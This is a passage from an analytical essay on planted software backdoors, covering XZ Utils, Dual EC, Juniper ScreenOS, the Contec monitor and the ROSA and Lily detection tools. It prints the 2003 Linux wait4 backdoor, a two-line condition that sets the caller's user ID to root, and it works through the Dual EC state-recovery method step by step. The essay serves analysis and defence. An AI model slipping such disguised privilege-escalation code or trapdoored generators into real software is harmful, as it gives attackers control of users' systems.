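This case comes closest to a pure example of what Schneier describes. The researchers say they misled the reviewers but kept the flaws out of the kernel, which would mean they subverted the process but not the product. The reaction suggests that people can consider this wrong even when no user is worse off.

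### Insiders, impostors and later users

Schneier's claim also fits much of what Tan did. Elsewhere in the essay, Schneier says that tricking people into handing over their login details is "much more a hack of trust and authority" than of a computer, and Tan got authority over XZ in a similar way. Tan then reviewed code, added test files and signed releases, as a maintainer is supposed to do. Open-source maintainers commonly accept work from people they know only by an email address, so even the false name may not have broken a rule.

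The claim fits less well when the planter is an insider who doesn't deceive any colleagues. If a company's managers order a maintenance password for their routers, the programmer who writes it is doing his job, and the process has produced what the people in charge of it wanted. Eric Allman wrote sendmail and decided on his own to put a backdoor in it, so there was hardly a process for him to subvert. Such planters mislead their customers. A lobbyist who gets a hidden tax provision into a bill is closer to Tan, at least if the legislators who vote for the bill don't know what the provision does. Planting a flaw hacks the process only if the planter gets it past people who were entitled to refuse it.

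The other half of the claim, that the code itself is not hacked, is harder to defend for XZ because more than one program was involved. Tan was a maintainer of XZ, so XZ arguably did what one of its designers intended. But OpenSSH's developers had no dealings with Tan, and they neither intended nor anticipated that a compression library would replace their signature check. By Schneier's own definition, that replacement looks like a hack of OpenSSH, and it happened every time an affected server started.

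Whoever planted the XZ backdoor deceived Collin and the distributions. Using it, by sending a signed command to a server, would have been a further act that wronged the server's owner. Schneier similarly says that the backdoors Chinese companies were suspected of putting into their network equipment would lie dormant until someone who knew of them used them. Anyone using the XZ backdoor needn't have been the planter, who could have sold the private key or lost it to a thief. A buyer would not have deceived Collin or subverted any process, but would still have got into computers without their owners' permission. Thompson, who had just explained how to plant a backdoor, thought that breaking into a computer should carry the same stigma as breaking into a neighbour's house, whether or not the neighbour had locked the door.

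Planting a backdoor and using it aren't always this separate, though. The XZ backdoor ran on Freund's computer without his consent and slowed down his logins, even though, as far as anyone knows, nobody ever sent it a command. If changing how someone's login program works without their permission wrongs them, whoever planted the backdoor had already wronged Freund and everyone else who installed it.

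## Whether a planted flaw can be told from a mistake

The XZ Utils backdoor was clearly deliberate, because nobody hides a program inside test files by mistake. Most flaws come with much less evidence of intent. If a router's login routine lacks a length check, strangers can get in the same way whether the programmer forgot the check or left it out on purpose. But on the view inferred from Schneier's definition, whether those strangers are hacking can depend on why the check is missing, so anyone who applies that view needs a way to find out.

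### Intentional, deniable and accidental

Thomas and Francillon sort suspicious flaws by how the program gets from the trigger to the payload. Sometimes the programmer wrote that step into the code, as with the login page that compares the visitor's text with a fixed phrase. In other cases the program gets there only because something goes wrong, such as overlong text spilling into neighbouring memory. They end up with three classes:

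- An intentional backdoor has the step from trigger to payload in its code.
- A deniable backdoor works through an apparent bug, but something outside the code suggests that someone planted it.
- An accidental vulnerability also works through a bug, and there is no evidence of any kind that anyone intended it.

They conclude that a deniable backdoor and an accidental vulnerability are technically indistinguishable, so evidence of intent has to come from somewhere other than the bug. They suggest checking the project's change log, if it has one, which can show who added the flaw and when. If only the finished program is available, an analyst can compare versions to find where the flaw first appeared, then ask whether there was a legitimate reason for that change. They also consider code suspicious if it does nothing except raise someone's privileges and normal use never reaches it. They admit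 that all these methods rely on human intuition and that none of them proves intent.

By definition, a vulnerability is accidental only if there is no evidence of intent and the developer was unaware of it. A flaw planted without a trace meets the first requirement but not the second. Investigators would presumably still classify it as accidental, so in practice the label means only that nobody has shown the flaw was deliberate.

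The intentional class is also less certain than it looks. Code that leads straight from a trigger to a payload shows that a programmer wrote it deliberately, but not why. Thomas and Francillon modelled eleven real backdoors, in six routers or families of routers, two cameras, two video recorders and a storage device. They classed all eleven as intentional and say that whoever built them should be held accountable. For most of the eleven, this is hard to dispute. A Quanta router, for example, gave anyone who sent it a particular word a command line with full privileges and no password.

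The storage device, Western Digital's My Cloud, is a more doubtful case. It gave administrator access to any visitor whose browser sent a cookie identifying them as an administrator. A programmer might write that as a deliberate backdoor, or because he didn't realize that visitors can edit their own cookies. Thomas and Francillon mention that manufacturers often describe such flaws as accidents or leftover debugging tools. They have an obvious motive to say so, but some are probably telling the truth.

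Researchers can also mistake ordinary code for a backdoor. Earlier work on backdoor detection had used hard-coded login details in the software of a TRENDnet device as a case study. Kokkonis and colleagues examined them while collecting real backdoors to test their detection tool, ROSA, and found that the code was a harmless workaround for owners who had left their username and password empty.

### Which backdoors get found

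The score of eleven out of eleven could mean that planters rarely disguise their backdoors, or that people mostly find the undisguised ones. The eleven cases come from published reports, largely by people who had taken a device's software apart, and a password comparison is easy to recognize once someone looks at it. If the same people had found a well-made bugdoor, they would probably have reported it as an ordinary vulnerability, so it would never have reached a list of backdoors.

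So the list can't show how common disguise is. Thomas and Francillon complain of a "sheer lack of real-world samples" of more complex backdoors. Kokkonis and colleagues had trouble finding even simple ones. They searched research papers, vulnerability databases and the news, examined 15 reports in depth, and ended up with seven authentic backdoors they could run.

A larger count, in GitHub's report *Securing the world's software* (2020), has the same limitation. GitHub, which hosts much of the world's open-source code, examined a random sample of 521 security advisories, the public notices that warn of vulnerabilities in a software package. It found that 17 per cent, or about 89, concerned explicitly malicious behaviour such as attempted backdoors. The great majority of these came from npm, the main collection of JavaScript packages. Most of the malicious packages had hardly any users, and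 they accounted for only 0.2 per cent of the alerts GitHub sent to developers.

GitHub concluded that most vulnerabilities are mistakes, which is very likely true. But the 83 per cent of advisories behind that conclusion were simply those that didn't concern explicit malice, and GitHub acknowledged in the same report that "a good backdoor can be indistinguishable from a normal programming mistake". Its analysts judged intent from circumstances, above all whether an attacker had taken over an account with permission to change the code. GitHub also found that vulnerabilities typically went unnoticed for more than four years, by which time it may be hard to find out why somebody wrote a particular line.

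### One equals sign in Linux

In November 2003 somebody tried to put a backdoor into the Linux kernel that looked like a typing error. Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) explains how it worked. The planter added two lines to wait4, a function that a program calls when it wants to wait for another program to finish:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
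        retval = -EINVAL;
```

They look like a routine check that returns an error when a program calls the function with a forbidden combination of options. In the C language, `==` tests whether two things are equal, while a single `=` sets the thing on the left to the value on the right. The last part of the first line appears to check whether the user's ID number is 0, but it changes that number to 0. On Linux, user 0 is root, the administrator who may do anything.

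When a program called wait4 with exactly the forbidden options, the first half of the condition was true, so the computer went on to the second half, which made the program's user root. In C, setting something to 0 yields 0, which counts as false, so the whole condition was false and the computer skipped the error. The program kept running with full control of the machine. With any other options, the computer never reached the second half, so ordinary programs would not have set off the backdoor.

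A missing approval record gave the attempt away, not the equals sign. Linux developers kept the master copy of their code in BitKeeper, where each change carried a pointer to the record of its approval. Some developers disliked BitKeeper, so the project also kept a duplicate in another system, CVS. On 5 November Larry McVoy, whose company made BitKeeper, noticed a change in the duplicate that had no such pointer and didn't exist in the master copy. Someone had apparently broken into the CVS server. According to Slashdot's *Linux Kernel Back-Door Hack Attempt Discovered* (2003), the scripts that copied code between the two systems had detected the change, and the planter had put the name of a long-standing developer, David Miller, on it.

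People studied the two lines only after that. On the kernel mailing list, one developer said they looked odd, and Chad Kitching asked whether they were an attempt to backdoor the kernel. McVoy agreed, pointed out the single equals sign, and admitted "I missed that." A Princeton computer scientist, writing the following week in the CITP blog post *Linux Backdoor Attempt Thwarted*, thought most programmers would have missed it on a casual reading. In *How a backdoor in the Linux kernel was thwarted, from RISKS*, McCullagh (2003) forwarded a message from Douglas Jones of the University of Iowa, who used the attempt as an example of what examiners of voting machine software would need to catch.

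Writing `=` for `==` is a common mistake in C, so the error alone doesn't show that this one was deliberate. On the mailing list, Tomas Szepe pointed to the extra brackets around `current->uid = 0`, which stop the compiler from warning about a likely mistake. The brackets are weak evidence of intent. As a reader of the Freedom to Tinker post observed, the line wouldn't compile without them, and many programmers also put brackets around ordinary comparisons.

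InfoQ's *Linux Backdoor* (2013) makes the better point that wait4 has no reason to deal with the user's identity. Another reader of the Freedom to Tinker post noticed that the line makes no sense even with the second equals sign restored, because it would then forbid a harmless combination of options only to the administrator. The strongest evidence that the flaw was planted is still the break-in and the false name. If Miller had submitted the same two lines through the normal process, his colleagues might well have called them a mistake.

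Thomas and Francillon cite the attempt as a case where a log of changes helps to identify a planted bug, but it doesn't fit their classes very well. The code itself contains the change of user, and the program reaches it without a memory error. Read strictly, their definition of an intentional backdoor would cover these lines even if a programmer had typed them by accident.

### How well disguise works

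Entrants to the Underhanded C Contest, which Scott Craver of Binghamton University started in 2005, had to write a program that did an ordinary task and also hid a specified malicious behavior. The code had to survive careful inspection, and the flaw had to look like an honest mistake if anyone found it. In 2015 the task was to write software for nuclear inspectors that compared readings from a warhead with a reference, and the hidden flaw had to let a fake warhead pass. The winning entries show that skilled people can write such code, but not how often reviewers would miss it, because the judges picked the best entries and already knew that each one contained a trick.

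A planted flaw can also be disguised in the compiled program, where an analyst reads machine instructions instead of source code. Dennis Andriesse and Herbert Bos built an example in 2014 by modifying Nginx, a popular web server. As Thomas and Francillon describe it, the trigger is a bug in which one function reads two variables before they are set, so they contain whatever the previous function left in that part of memory. An attacker can control those values with a malformed web request, and the right values make the server run hidden code.

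That code is hidden inside the program's ordinary instructions. Instructions for common Intel-type processors vary in length, and nothing in the bytes marks where one instruction ends and the next begins. If the processor starts reading one byte later than usual, the same bytes can form different instructions. Andriesse and Bos arranged fragments of the program so that their bytes form ordinary instructions when read from the normal starting point and make up the payload when read from another.

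Thomas and Francillon consider the Nginx trigger deniable because programmers do forget to initialize variables. They say the payload, if anybody finds it, is arguably intentional, since useful instructions are unlikely to line up by chance in the gaps between other instructions. The planter could have included only the bug, which would have been easier to deny, but Thomas and Francillon note that someone who plants a bug alone has no control over what people later do with it.

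Few experiments measure how well reviewers find flaws that researchers know to be there. In *An Empirical Study on the Effectiveness of Security Code Review* (2013), Anne Edmundson and colleagues hired 30 developers to review a small web application with seven known vulnerabilities. None found all seven, and the more experienced developers didn't necessarily do better. In *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?* (2021), Larissa Braz and colleagues ran an online experiment in which 146 participants reviewed code with a single flaw, of a kind the researchers regard as easy to detect. Many participants who had missed the flaw found it after being warned that it was there, but 60 of the 146 still couldn't.

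Nobody had tried to disguise the flaws in either experiment as innocent code, so reviewers would presumably do worse against someone skilled at planting them. But the participants spent a short time on unfamiliar code, whereas maintainers know their own projects, and on a large project several of them may look at the same change.

### Searching by behaviour

Another approach is to run the program and watch what it does, which is less vulnerable to code that merely looks innocent. ROSA, the 2025 tool that compares similar inputs, first fuzzes the program with partly random inputs for about a minute to collect examples of normal behaviour. It then runs the fuzzer for hours and compares each new input with the stored example that took the most similar path through the program.

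Kokkonis and colleagues illustrate the comparison with a program that has only four possible steps. A new input makes the program run all four. Stored example A made it run steps 1 and 3, and stored example B only step 2. The new input differs from A in two steps and from B in three, so ROSA compares it with A. ROSA then compares their system calls, the requests a program makes to the operating system, such as opening a file or starting another program. The new input made the program open and read something, while A only made it open something. Since similar paths should lead to similar requests, ROSA reports the new input as suspicious.

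The researchers ran ROSA ten times on each of their 17 test backdoors, for eight hours each time. It missed the backdoor in a Belkin router in all ten runs, so they did ten more eight-hour runs with better starting inputs, and seven succeeded. Overall, ROSA succeeded in 156 of 180 runs. In the other 24, the fuzzer never produced an input that triggers the backdoor. Whenever the fuzzer did produce one, ROSA recognized it.

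Eight hours is too long for a project that accepts several changes a day, and a person has to look at every report. For *Not In My Git Yard*, Kokkonis and colleagues built a faster tool called Lily, which examines only the difference between two versions of a program. It runs the fuzzer for ten minutes and raises an alarm if an input makes the new version produce a combination of system calls that is unusual for that version and that the old version does not produce from the same input.

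Using both conditions, Lily raised false alarms in 0.2 per cent of its runs on harmless commits. It would have done so in 14 per cent of them using only the first condition, and in 10 per cent using only the second.

Lily also shows the reviewer where to look. The backdoored vsFTPd release of 2011 differed from the previous release by 1,407 lines across five files. Lily narrowed these changes to seven lines in one file, which a reviewer could recognize as opening a command line to remote users.

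| | ROSA | Lily |
|---|---|---|
| What it examines | A finished program | The change from one version to the next |
| Length of a run | 8 hours | 10 minutes |
| Test set | 17 backdoors | 13 backdoored and 432 harmless commits; 50 backdoored and 50 harmless releases |
| Runs that found the backdoor | 156 of 180 (87%) | Commits: 233 of 260 (90%). Releases: 828 of 1,000 (83%) |
| False alarms | On average about 7 inputs to check by hand | Commits: 17 of 8,640 runs (0.2%). Releases: 43 of 1,000 runs (4.3%) |
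| What it can't see | Triggers the fuzzer doesn't reach, including cryptographic ones | The same, and any backdoor already in the old version |

Of the 43 false alarms on releases, 40 came from two releases of one sound library, so the rate for most projects should be lower than 4.3 per cent. The rate for commits is much smaller, but planted backdoors are so rare that false alarms would still outnumber real ones. A project with 10,000 commits, one of them backdoored, could expect about 20 false alarms and a 90 per cent chance that the backdoor is flagged. Checking that many alarms over the life of a project is manageable, but a maintainer who has dismissed many false ones may check the next less carefully.

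A more serious weakness is that the fuzzer never runs some of the code. In 337 commits that changed code, Lily's ten minutes of testing reached on average only about 32 per cent of the lines it could have reached, mostly because the projects' own test setups were limited. Neither tool can activate a trigger that needs a private key, like the one in XZ Utils, because the fuzzer would have to forge a signature.

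An attacker could also try to corrupt the collection of inputs from which Lily learns what is normal. When the researchers added 100 inputs that triggered the backdoor, Lily's detection rate fell to 54 per cent for commits and 46 per cent for releases. A stricter mode cancelled the effect, but raised false alarms to 3 and 18 per cent respectively.

Neither tool detects intent. A debugging entrance left in by accident would trigger the same alarm as one planted by a spy, and a person would have to decide which it was. Kokkonis and colleagues leave bugdoors to ordinary bug-finding tools, which can catch them because bugdoors tend to make programs crash or misuse memory. Those tools can't tell whether a flaw was deliberate either. The problem may be worse in machine learning, because cryptographers have described backdoors in models that no efficient test can find.

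Knowing whether a flaw was planted may not matter much to someone who only wants a safe program, since the same patch removes it either way, but it matters to anyone deciding whether to trust the programmer's other work.

### The Contec patient monitor

In early 2025 two groups of specialists examined the same device and disagreed about whether it had a backdoor. The device was the Contec CMS8000, a monitor that hospitals use to track patients' heart rate, blood pressure and other vital signs. Its manufacturer, Contec, is Chinese, and other companies resell it under their own names. *Contec CMS8000 Contains a Backdoor* (2025), a fact sheet published on 30 January by the US cybersecurity agency CISA, reports on three versions of the monitor's built-in software. All three had what CISA called an embedded backdoor function, which used a fixed internet address, and a flaw that leaked patient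 data. CISA classified the function as Hidden Functionality, MITRE's category for undocumented features.

The agency worded its formal advisory more cautiously. Security Affairs' *CISA FDA warned hidden backdoor in Contec CMS8000* quotes the advisory as saying that the monitor bypasses its own network settings to send remote access requests to the fixed address, and that this "could serve as a backdoor". Whoever controlled that address might be able to upload files to the monitor and overwrite existing ones.

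The security company Claroty also studied the software and concluded in *Do the CONTEC CMS8000 Patient Monitors Contain a Chinese Backdoor?* that the function was most likely an insecure design, not a hidden backdoor. Its main reason was that the address appears in the operating manuals of Contec and its resellers. According to Radiflow's *Bug or feature the backdoor in Contec CMS8000 patient monitor*, a hospital following the manuals would set up a central management computer on its internal network and give it that address. The monitor would then send its readings to the nurses' station and get its updates from there.

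This explanation is plausible, but the address isn't reserved for private networks, so on the internet it can belong to somebody else. Radiflow reports that the monitor automatically connects to it when it starts up and begins sending patient information. If a hospital hasn't set up the central computer and doesn't block outgoing traffic, the readings may go to a stranger.

SecurityWeek's *Contec Patient Monitors Not Malicious, but Still Pose Big Risk to Healthcare* dropped Claroty's "most likely" and stated that the monitors contain no malicious backdoor. The manual shows only that Contec didn't conceal the address, which doesn't rule out malice. Someone who planned to spy on hospitals would have little reason to print the address, but a planter who wanted deniability might find a documented feature with poor security more useful than a secret one. Nothing published so far shows that Contec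 reasoned this way.

The connection is written into the software, which points to an intentional backdoor under Thomas and Francillon's classes, and Claroty doesn't deny that a programmer put the address there on purpose. The classes don't settle the dispute, because the two sides disagree about what the address was for and whether the hospitals knew about it.

The manual matters more under Zdziarski's test, which depends on what the maker told the owner. Even so, a hospital could read the instruction to give its central computer a certain address without realizing that the monitor would contact the same address on the open internet. That hospital would have known about the address but not agreed to the connection. Claroty argued that the lack of malicious intent should change how urgently hospitals deal with the flaw. The maker's intent would matter less in describing a stranger who took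 over the address and rewrote the software on a patient's monitor, because no hospital had given him permission.

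## Whether a planted flaw stays with those it was planted for

A badly configured Contec monitor will send its readings to whoever controls one internet address. Someone who plants a flaw for his own use needs a better way to restrict it to the people he has in mind. Otherwise, strangers will exploit a flaw that he planted on purpose but didn't intend for them.

### The NOBUS claim

The US National Security Agency (NSA) uses the term NOBUS, short for "nobody but us", for a weakness it believes no one else can exploit. In *Nobody But Us*, Buchanan traces the idea to a conflict between the agency's two jobs, reading foreign messages and protecting American ones. In the Second World War the two sides used different cipher machines, so the Allies could attack the German Enigma without weakening the American SIGABA. Today governments, companies and terrorists use the same phones and encryption.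 The NOBUS approach is to close the weaknesses that rivals could exploit and keep the ones that only the United States can.

Sometimes the advantage is money. Michael Hayden, a former director of the NSA, gave the example of a flaw that takes "four acres" of supercomputers to exploit, and said the agency had no legal or ethical duty to get such a flaw patched. Many encryption systems share the same few large prime numbers, and Buchanan cites an estimate that a machine costing several hundred million dollars could break about one a year. Breaking one would open two-thirds of the world's virtual private networks (VPNs), the encrypted links companies use to connect offices and staff over the internet. But rivals can spend money too, and foreign agencies keep their computing power secret.

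In other cases the advantage is only that nobody else has noticed the flaw. The NSA reportedly exploited a flaw in Windows for five years with a tool called ETERNALBLUE, until a group calling itself the Shadow Brokers obtained and published it. Microsoft had already issued a patch, probably after a tip from the agency. But a month after the tool was published, attackers used a version of it to infect hundreds of thousands of unpatched computers, which forced shutdowns across Britain's National Health Service.

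Someone who plants a flaw, unlike someone who finds one, can design it so that exploiting it requires a secret. A post on Lawfare, a site about national security law, argues that such a flaw would be harder for others to exploit than an ordinary vulnerability. The post concedes that planting a flaw always weakens the system somewhat, but considers this acceptable if the secret is likely to stay secret for a long time. The XZ Utils backdoor relied on a private key in this way, and a digital signature can also trigger a backdoor in a machine-learning model.

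### How Dual EC works

The NSA appears to have tried this with Dual EC, a random-number generator that NIST standardized in June 2006. Encryption software uses some random numbers as secret keys and sends others openly, as one-time values called nonces. A generator starts from a small amount of real randomness, its initial state, and uses it to produce a long series of numbers. The state has to stay secret because anyone who learns it can calculate every later output.

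Dual EC does its arithmetic with points on an elliptic curve. Each point is a pair of numbers (x, y) that satisfies the curve's equation, and there is a rule for adding two points to get a third. Multiplying a point by 5 means adding five copies of it together. A computer can quickly multiply a point by an enormous number, but nobody knows a practical way to work out the multiplier from the point and its multiple.

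The standard fixes two points, P and Q. If s₁ is the current state, and x( ) means the x-coordinate of a point, then:

- the output is r₁ = x(s₁Q)
- the next state is s₂ = x(s₁P)

The generator removes the first 16 of the output's 256 bits and releases the other 240.

Bernstein, Lange and Niederhagen (2015), in *Dual EC*, explain what somebody can do who knows a number d such that P = dQ. Suppose first that he sees the whole of r₁. This is the x-coordinate of the point s₁Q, and the curve's equation gives him the y-coordinate, apart from its sign. He now has the point, though he doesn't know s₁. He multiplies it by d:

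d(s₁Q) = s₁(dQ) = s₁P

The x-coordinate of s₁P is the next state, s₂. If he picked the wrong sign for y, he gets the mirror image of s₁P, which has the same x-coordinate. From then on he can run the generator himself and get the same numbers as its owner.

Removing 16 bits hardly slows the attacker down, because they can have only 2¹⁶ = 65,536 values and he can try each one. About half don't belong to any point on the curve. For the rest, he calculates what the generator would do next and checks it against something he can see. Each further missing bit doubles the work, so a generator that released far fewer bits would have had no usable backdoor. In March 2006 an academic cryptographer reported another fault to NIST, that the outputs weren't random enough. Releasing fewer bits was the obvious remedy for that too, but NIST standardized the generator without making the change.

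### Dual EC with small numbers

The calculation also works on a curve small enough to check by hand. The curve's equation is y² = x³ + 2x + 2, and only remainders after division by 17 are kept, so every coordinate lies between 0 and 16. The point Q is (5, 1). Its multiples repeat every 19 steps, so 21Q is the same point as 2Q. The table gives the x-coordinates of the multiples, each of which appears twice because mirror-image points share an x-coordinate.

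| Multiple of Q | 1 or 18 | 2 or 17 | 3 or 16 | 4 or 15 | 5 or 14 | 6 or 13 | 7 or 12 | 8 or 11 | 9 or 10 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| x-coordinate | 5 | 6 | 10 | 3 | 9 | 16 | 0 | 13 | 7 |

The planter chooses d = 3, publishes Q and P = 3Q = (10, 6), and keeps the 3 to himself. To imitate the missing bits, this generator releases only the last digit of each output. Its owner starts it with the secret number 7:

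| Step | State | Full output | Digit released |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | x(7P) = x(21Q) = x(2Q) = 6 | x(6Q) = 16 | 6 |
| 2 | x(6P) = x(18Q) = 5 | x(5Q) = 9 | 9 |
| 3 | x(5P) = x(15Q) = 3 | x(3Q) = 10 | 0 |

An eavesdropper who knows d sees the 6. The full output must have been 6 or 16, so he tries both:

- If it was 6, the point was (6, 3). Three times this point has the x-coordinate 16, so the next state would be 16 and the next digit 0.
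- If it was 16, the point was (16, 13). Three times this point has the x-coordinate 5, so the next state would be 5 and the next digit 9.

The next digit is 9, so the state is now 5. He can calculate the third digit, 0, and every digit after that before the generator produces them.

An outsider could find d here by trying 1, 2 and 3. The real curve has about 2²⁵⁶ points, too many to try one by one.

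### Whether anyone has the number

Nobody can tell from P and Q whether someone knows d. In October 2004 John Kelsey of NIST asked where Q came from. Don Johnson, who had presented the generator at a NIST workshop that summer, replied that Q was essentially the public key for a random private key. Whoever kept that private key could calculate d. Johnson added that one could choose Q to avoid this, but that the NSA had rejected the idea and he wasn't allowed to discuss it publicly.

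A March 2007 revision made the backdoor more reliable. The original version let software mix extra input into the state before each request, which often broke the link between an output and the next state. The revision added a state update at the end of each request, before any extra input was mixed in. The official reason was to protect earlier outputs if someone stole the state, but Bernstein and colleagues point out that a simpler change would have done this without repairing the backdoor.

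Two Microsoft researchers, Dan Shumow and Niels Ferguson, publicly described the possible backdoor in August 2007. NIST kept the generator, saying it had no evidence that anyone had the secret numbers. It also refused to certify products that used any other P and Q. In September 2013 the New York Times reported that leaked NSA memos appeared to confirm that the agency had engineered the weakness. Reuters reported that December that the agency had paid the security company RSA 10 million dollars to make Dual EC the default in one of its products. In 2014 a former NSA official said the agency had wanted the generator for its own use and expected nobody else to adopt anything so slow, which is hard to reconcile with the payment to RSA.

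All this is strong evidence that the NSA wanted a backdoor, though nobody has ever published d. To test the attack, researchers had to replace P and Q in four encryption libraries with points whose d they knew. They recovered the state of one RSA library in under three seconds on 16 processors. When a connection revealed less of the output, the search took one to three hours in most cases.

As far as anyone knows, no outsider has used the original Dual EC backdoor. Such use would be hard to discover, because an eavesdropper can record traffic and decrypt it later without touching either computer, and a spy who stole d would have good reason to keep quiet.

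### Sabotage that locks others out

Adam Young and Moti Yung had studied backdoors of this kind since the 1990s, under the name kleptography. In their scheme, the planter replaces an honest encryption program with one whose outputs look the same to any efficient test but leak the user's private key to him alone. One of their examples uses RSA encryption, whose public key contains the product of two secret primes. The altered program encrypts one prime with the planter's own public key and hides the result in the leading digits of the product. The planter decrypts those digits to recover that prime, then divides the product by it to get the other. Someone who takes the program apart will discover the backdoor but still can't use it.

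Schneier, Fredrikson and colleagues (2015) note in *Surreptitiously Weakening Cryptographic Systems* that swapping in an altered program suits sealed hardware best, because the planter doesn't try to hide the change from someone who reads the program. The weakness in Dual EC was in the standard, so software that followed the standard perfectly had it too, without any program being swapped.

"Surreptitiously Weakening Cryptographic Systems" proposes ten criteria for comparing acts of cryptographic sabotage, scored from the saboteur's point of view. It also applies them to accidents, which show what a saboteur could do on purpose. In 2006 a developer working on Debian removed two lines from an encryption library because a testing tool flagged them. The lines supplied most of the library's randomness, so for two years affected computers could generate only 32,767 different key pairs.

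| Criterion | What it measures | Dual EC | Debian |
|---|---|---|---|
| Undetectability | How hard the weakness is to find | Medium | High |
| Lack of conspiracy | How few people and resources it takes | Low | High |
| Deniability | How easily it passes for a mistake | Low | High |
| Ease of use | How little work an attack takes | Medium | Medium to high |
| Severity | How directly it gives the attacker what he wants | Medium | High |
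| Durability | How hard it is to remove once known | Medium to high | Low to medium |
| Monitorability | Whether the saboteur can see others using it | Low | Medium |
| Scale | How many people it exposes | Low | High |
| Precision | Whether the saboteur can weaken only his targets | Low | Medium |
| Control | Whether he can keep others from using it | High | Low |

The entries with a range are ones where the paper rates the same case differently in different places.

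Control, the NOBUS ("nobody but us") criterion, is whether only the planter can exploit the flaw. Dual EC scores well on control and badly on deniability, and the Debian flaw does the reverse. The two criteria conflict because restricting a flaw to its planter takes deliberate design, which is hard to pass off as a mistake.

Lotus Notes 4, an office program of the 1990s, fits the same pattern. US export rules limited encryption keys in products sold abroad to 40 bits. Lotus used 64-bit keys, but encrypted 24 of the bits with an NSA public key and attached them to each message. The NSA then had to guess only 40 bits, while guessing all 64 took anyone else nearly 17 million times as much work. Lotus described this in its technical documentation and advertised it, so it had high control and no deniability. But Schneier and colleagues examined only a handful of cases, several of them apparently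 accidents, and they call their ratings subjective.

They also warn that control is lost if the secret leaks or someone steals it. Ten months after the date on their paper, a firewall maker disclosed that someone had taken control without the old secret.

### The lock that someone changed

On 17 December 2015, Juniper Networks announced that it had found "unauthorized code" in ScreenOS, the operating system of its NetScreen firewalls, which also ran VPNs. The code could let an attacker log in as an administrator or decrypt VPN traffic. Juniper gave few details, so Checkoway, Maskiewicz and colleagues (2016) reverse-engineered the software to find out what had happened, in *A Systematic Analysis of the Juniper Dual EC Incident*.

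Very little had changed in ScreenOS, which used Dual EC. From August or September 2012, its official releases contained a different Q and a matching change to a built-in self-test. Whoever chose the new Q presumably knew the corresponding d. A separate change, which reached customers by April 2013, added a fixed password that gave anyone who knew it full control of the firewall.

Juniper had started using Dual EC in October 2008. It said in 2013 that this was safe because it used its own Q instead of the one in the standard, and because it fed the output into a second generator, which would have hidden the numbers an eavesdropper needs. *Where Did I Leave My Keys?*, a shorter version of the study, explains why the second generator never ran. It was inside a loop that should have repeated until a counter reached 32, but the routine just before the loop used the same counter and left it at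 32, so the loop was skipped. That routine also left raw Dual EC output where the rest of the software read finished numbers. Several experienced researchers who suspected a bug there read the code without noticing it.

Other changes in the 2008 release also helped eavesdroppers. Juniper lengthened its devices' nonces, which were sent openly, from 20 bytes to 32. The old nonces would have been too short, because an attacker needs to see about 26 bytes of a single output for the search to be practical. The devices also began to prepare nonces in advance, so a connection's nonce often came out of the generator before its secret key. An eavesdropper could then work forward from the nonce to the key.

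The researchers bought a Juniper device and installed a copy of ScreenOS with their own Q. They made three VPN connections with different settings and decrypted each from its recorded traffic.

Researchers couldn't tell from the software how Juniper had settled on Dual EC, how it had generated its original Q, or whether anyone had ever known the matching secret number, d. Juniper would not say, even after a congressional hearing. If nobody knew d, ScreenOS had a badly designed generator from 2008 but no working backdoor until the intruder replaced Q in 2012. If somebody did know it, the backdoor was there from 2008, and replacing Q changed who could use it.

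Buchanan thinks the NSA probably placed a backdoor in ScreenOS in 2008. His evidence is circumstantial. The agency had apparently compromised the Dual EC standard, it had a secret programme for weakening commercial encryption with companies' help, and Juniper's customers included likely targets. Juniper denied acting at the agency's direction. Juniper's use of its own Q also counts against the theory, because a d that fits the standard Q wouldn't fit a different one, so the NSA would also have had to supply or influence Juniper's Q. Buchanan attributes the 2012 change to someone else, quite likely a foreign intelligence service.

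If he is right, the NOBUS claim failed here even though the mathematics held. Nobody had to calculate or steal the original d.

### The telephone companies' wiretap systems

US law requires telephone companies to be able to tap a customer's calls when a court orders it, and the companies run systems for this. In autumn 2024, news outlets reported that hackers linked to China had gained access to some of these systems, in a campaign investigators call Salt Typhoon. That November, the FBI and CISA said the intruders had copied information that was subject to court-ordered requests from law enforcement.

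According to CNA's *US was warned of telecom security risks years before Salt Typhoon*, US officials have alleged that the hackers targeted nine companies, including Verizon and AT&T, and stole "telephone audio intercepts" and many call records. "Intercepts" could mean recordings made for the police or calls the hackers tapped themselves.

The hackers don't seem to have got in through the wiretap systems. Herald Business' *Congress says regulatory gaps let Chinese hackers into US telecom networks* reports that they exploited flaws in equipment from Fortinet and Cisco. In August 2026 a congressional committee described another possible route, through equipment that three Chinese state-owned carriers had kept in American data centres after regulators barred them from connecting directly to US networks. DiMolfetta (2026), in *Chinese telecoms kept footholds in US despite crackdowns, probe finds*,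 adds that one network with ties to these carriers appeared in routes to Salt Typhoon's servers. This suggests but doesn't prove that the hackers got in that way. In June 2022 CISA had also received a report it had commissioned, which warned that attackers could compromise the national networks from anywhere in the world. CISA reportedly withheld the report from the public for four years.

Hackers who could get this far into the networks would have done serious damage even without the wiretap systems. But those systems hold information about whom the government is watching, which is especially valuable to a foreign intelligence service.

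### The dispute over mandated access

Since 2014 US law enforcement officials have warned that they are "going dark". A court can order a wiretap, but the recording is useless if only the sender and recipient have the keys to decrypt it. The officials want technology companies to design products so that investigators can read messages with a court order. They would argue that judges already approve house searches and wiretaps on ordinary telephone lines, and that encryption shouldn't exempt a conversation from the same kind of order.

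Such a system needs a key that only the authorities can use. The NSA's Clipper chip of 1993 encrypted each user's keys with another key known to the US government. Dual EC could work similarly, with d as the government's key. Two employees of the Canadian company Certicom described this in a January 2005 patent application, including its use by "trusted law enforcement agents". They also explained how to choose Q so that nobody would have the key.

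Supporters can also point out that investigators without such a key turn to hacking. Buchanan notes that the FBI has hacked thousands of people around the world and keeps unpatched flaws for its own use. An entrance supervised by a court might do less harm than giving police a reason to leave flaws in everyone's software. On the other hand, investigators can still get evidence when people use encryption. It usually hides what people say but not whom they contact, and many people store backups with companies that can decrypt them and have to hand them over.

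Critics have long objected that someone may steal or leak the key. *Where Did I Leave My Keys?* adds that an intruder can replace it, as someone did at Juniper. The outputs looked just as random after the change, so neither customers nor Juniper's tests could have detected the replacement by examining them. The researchers argue that an attacker would generally have to make much larger changes to a product with no access mechanism, and that people are more likely to notice larger changes.

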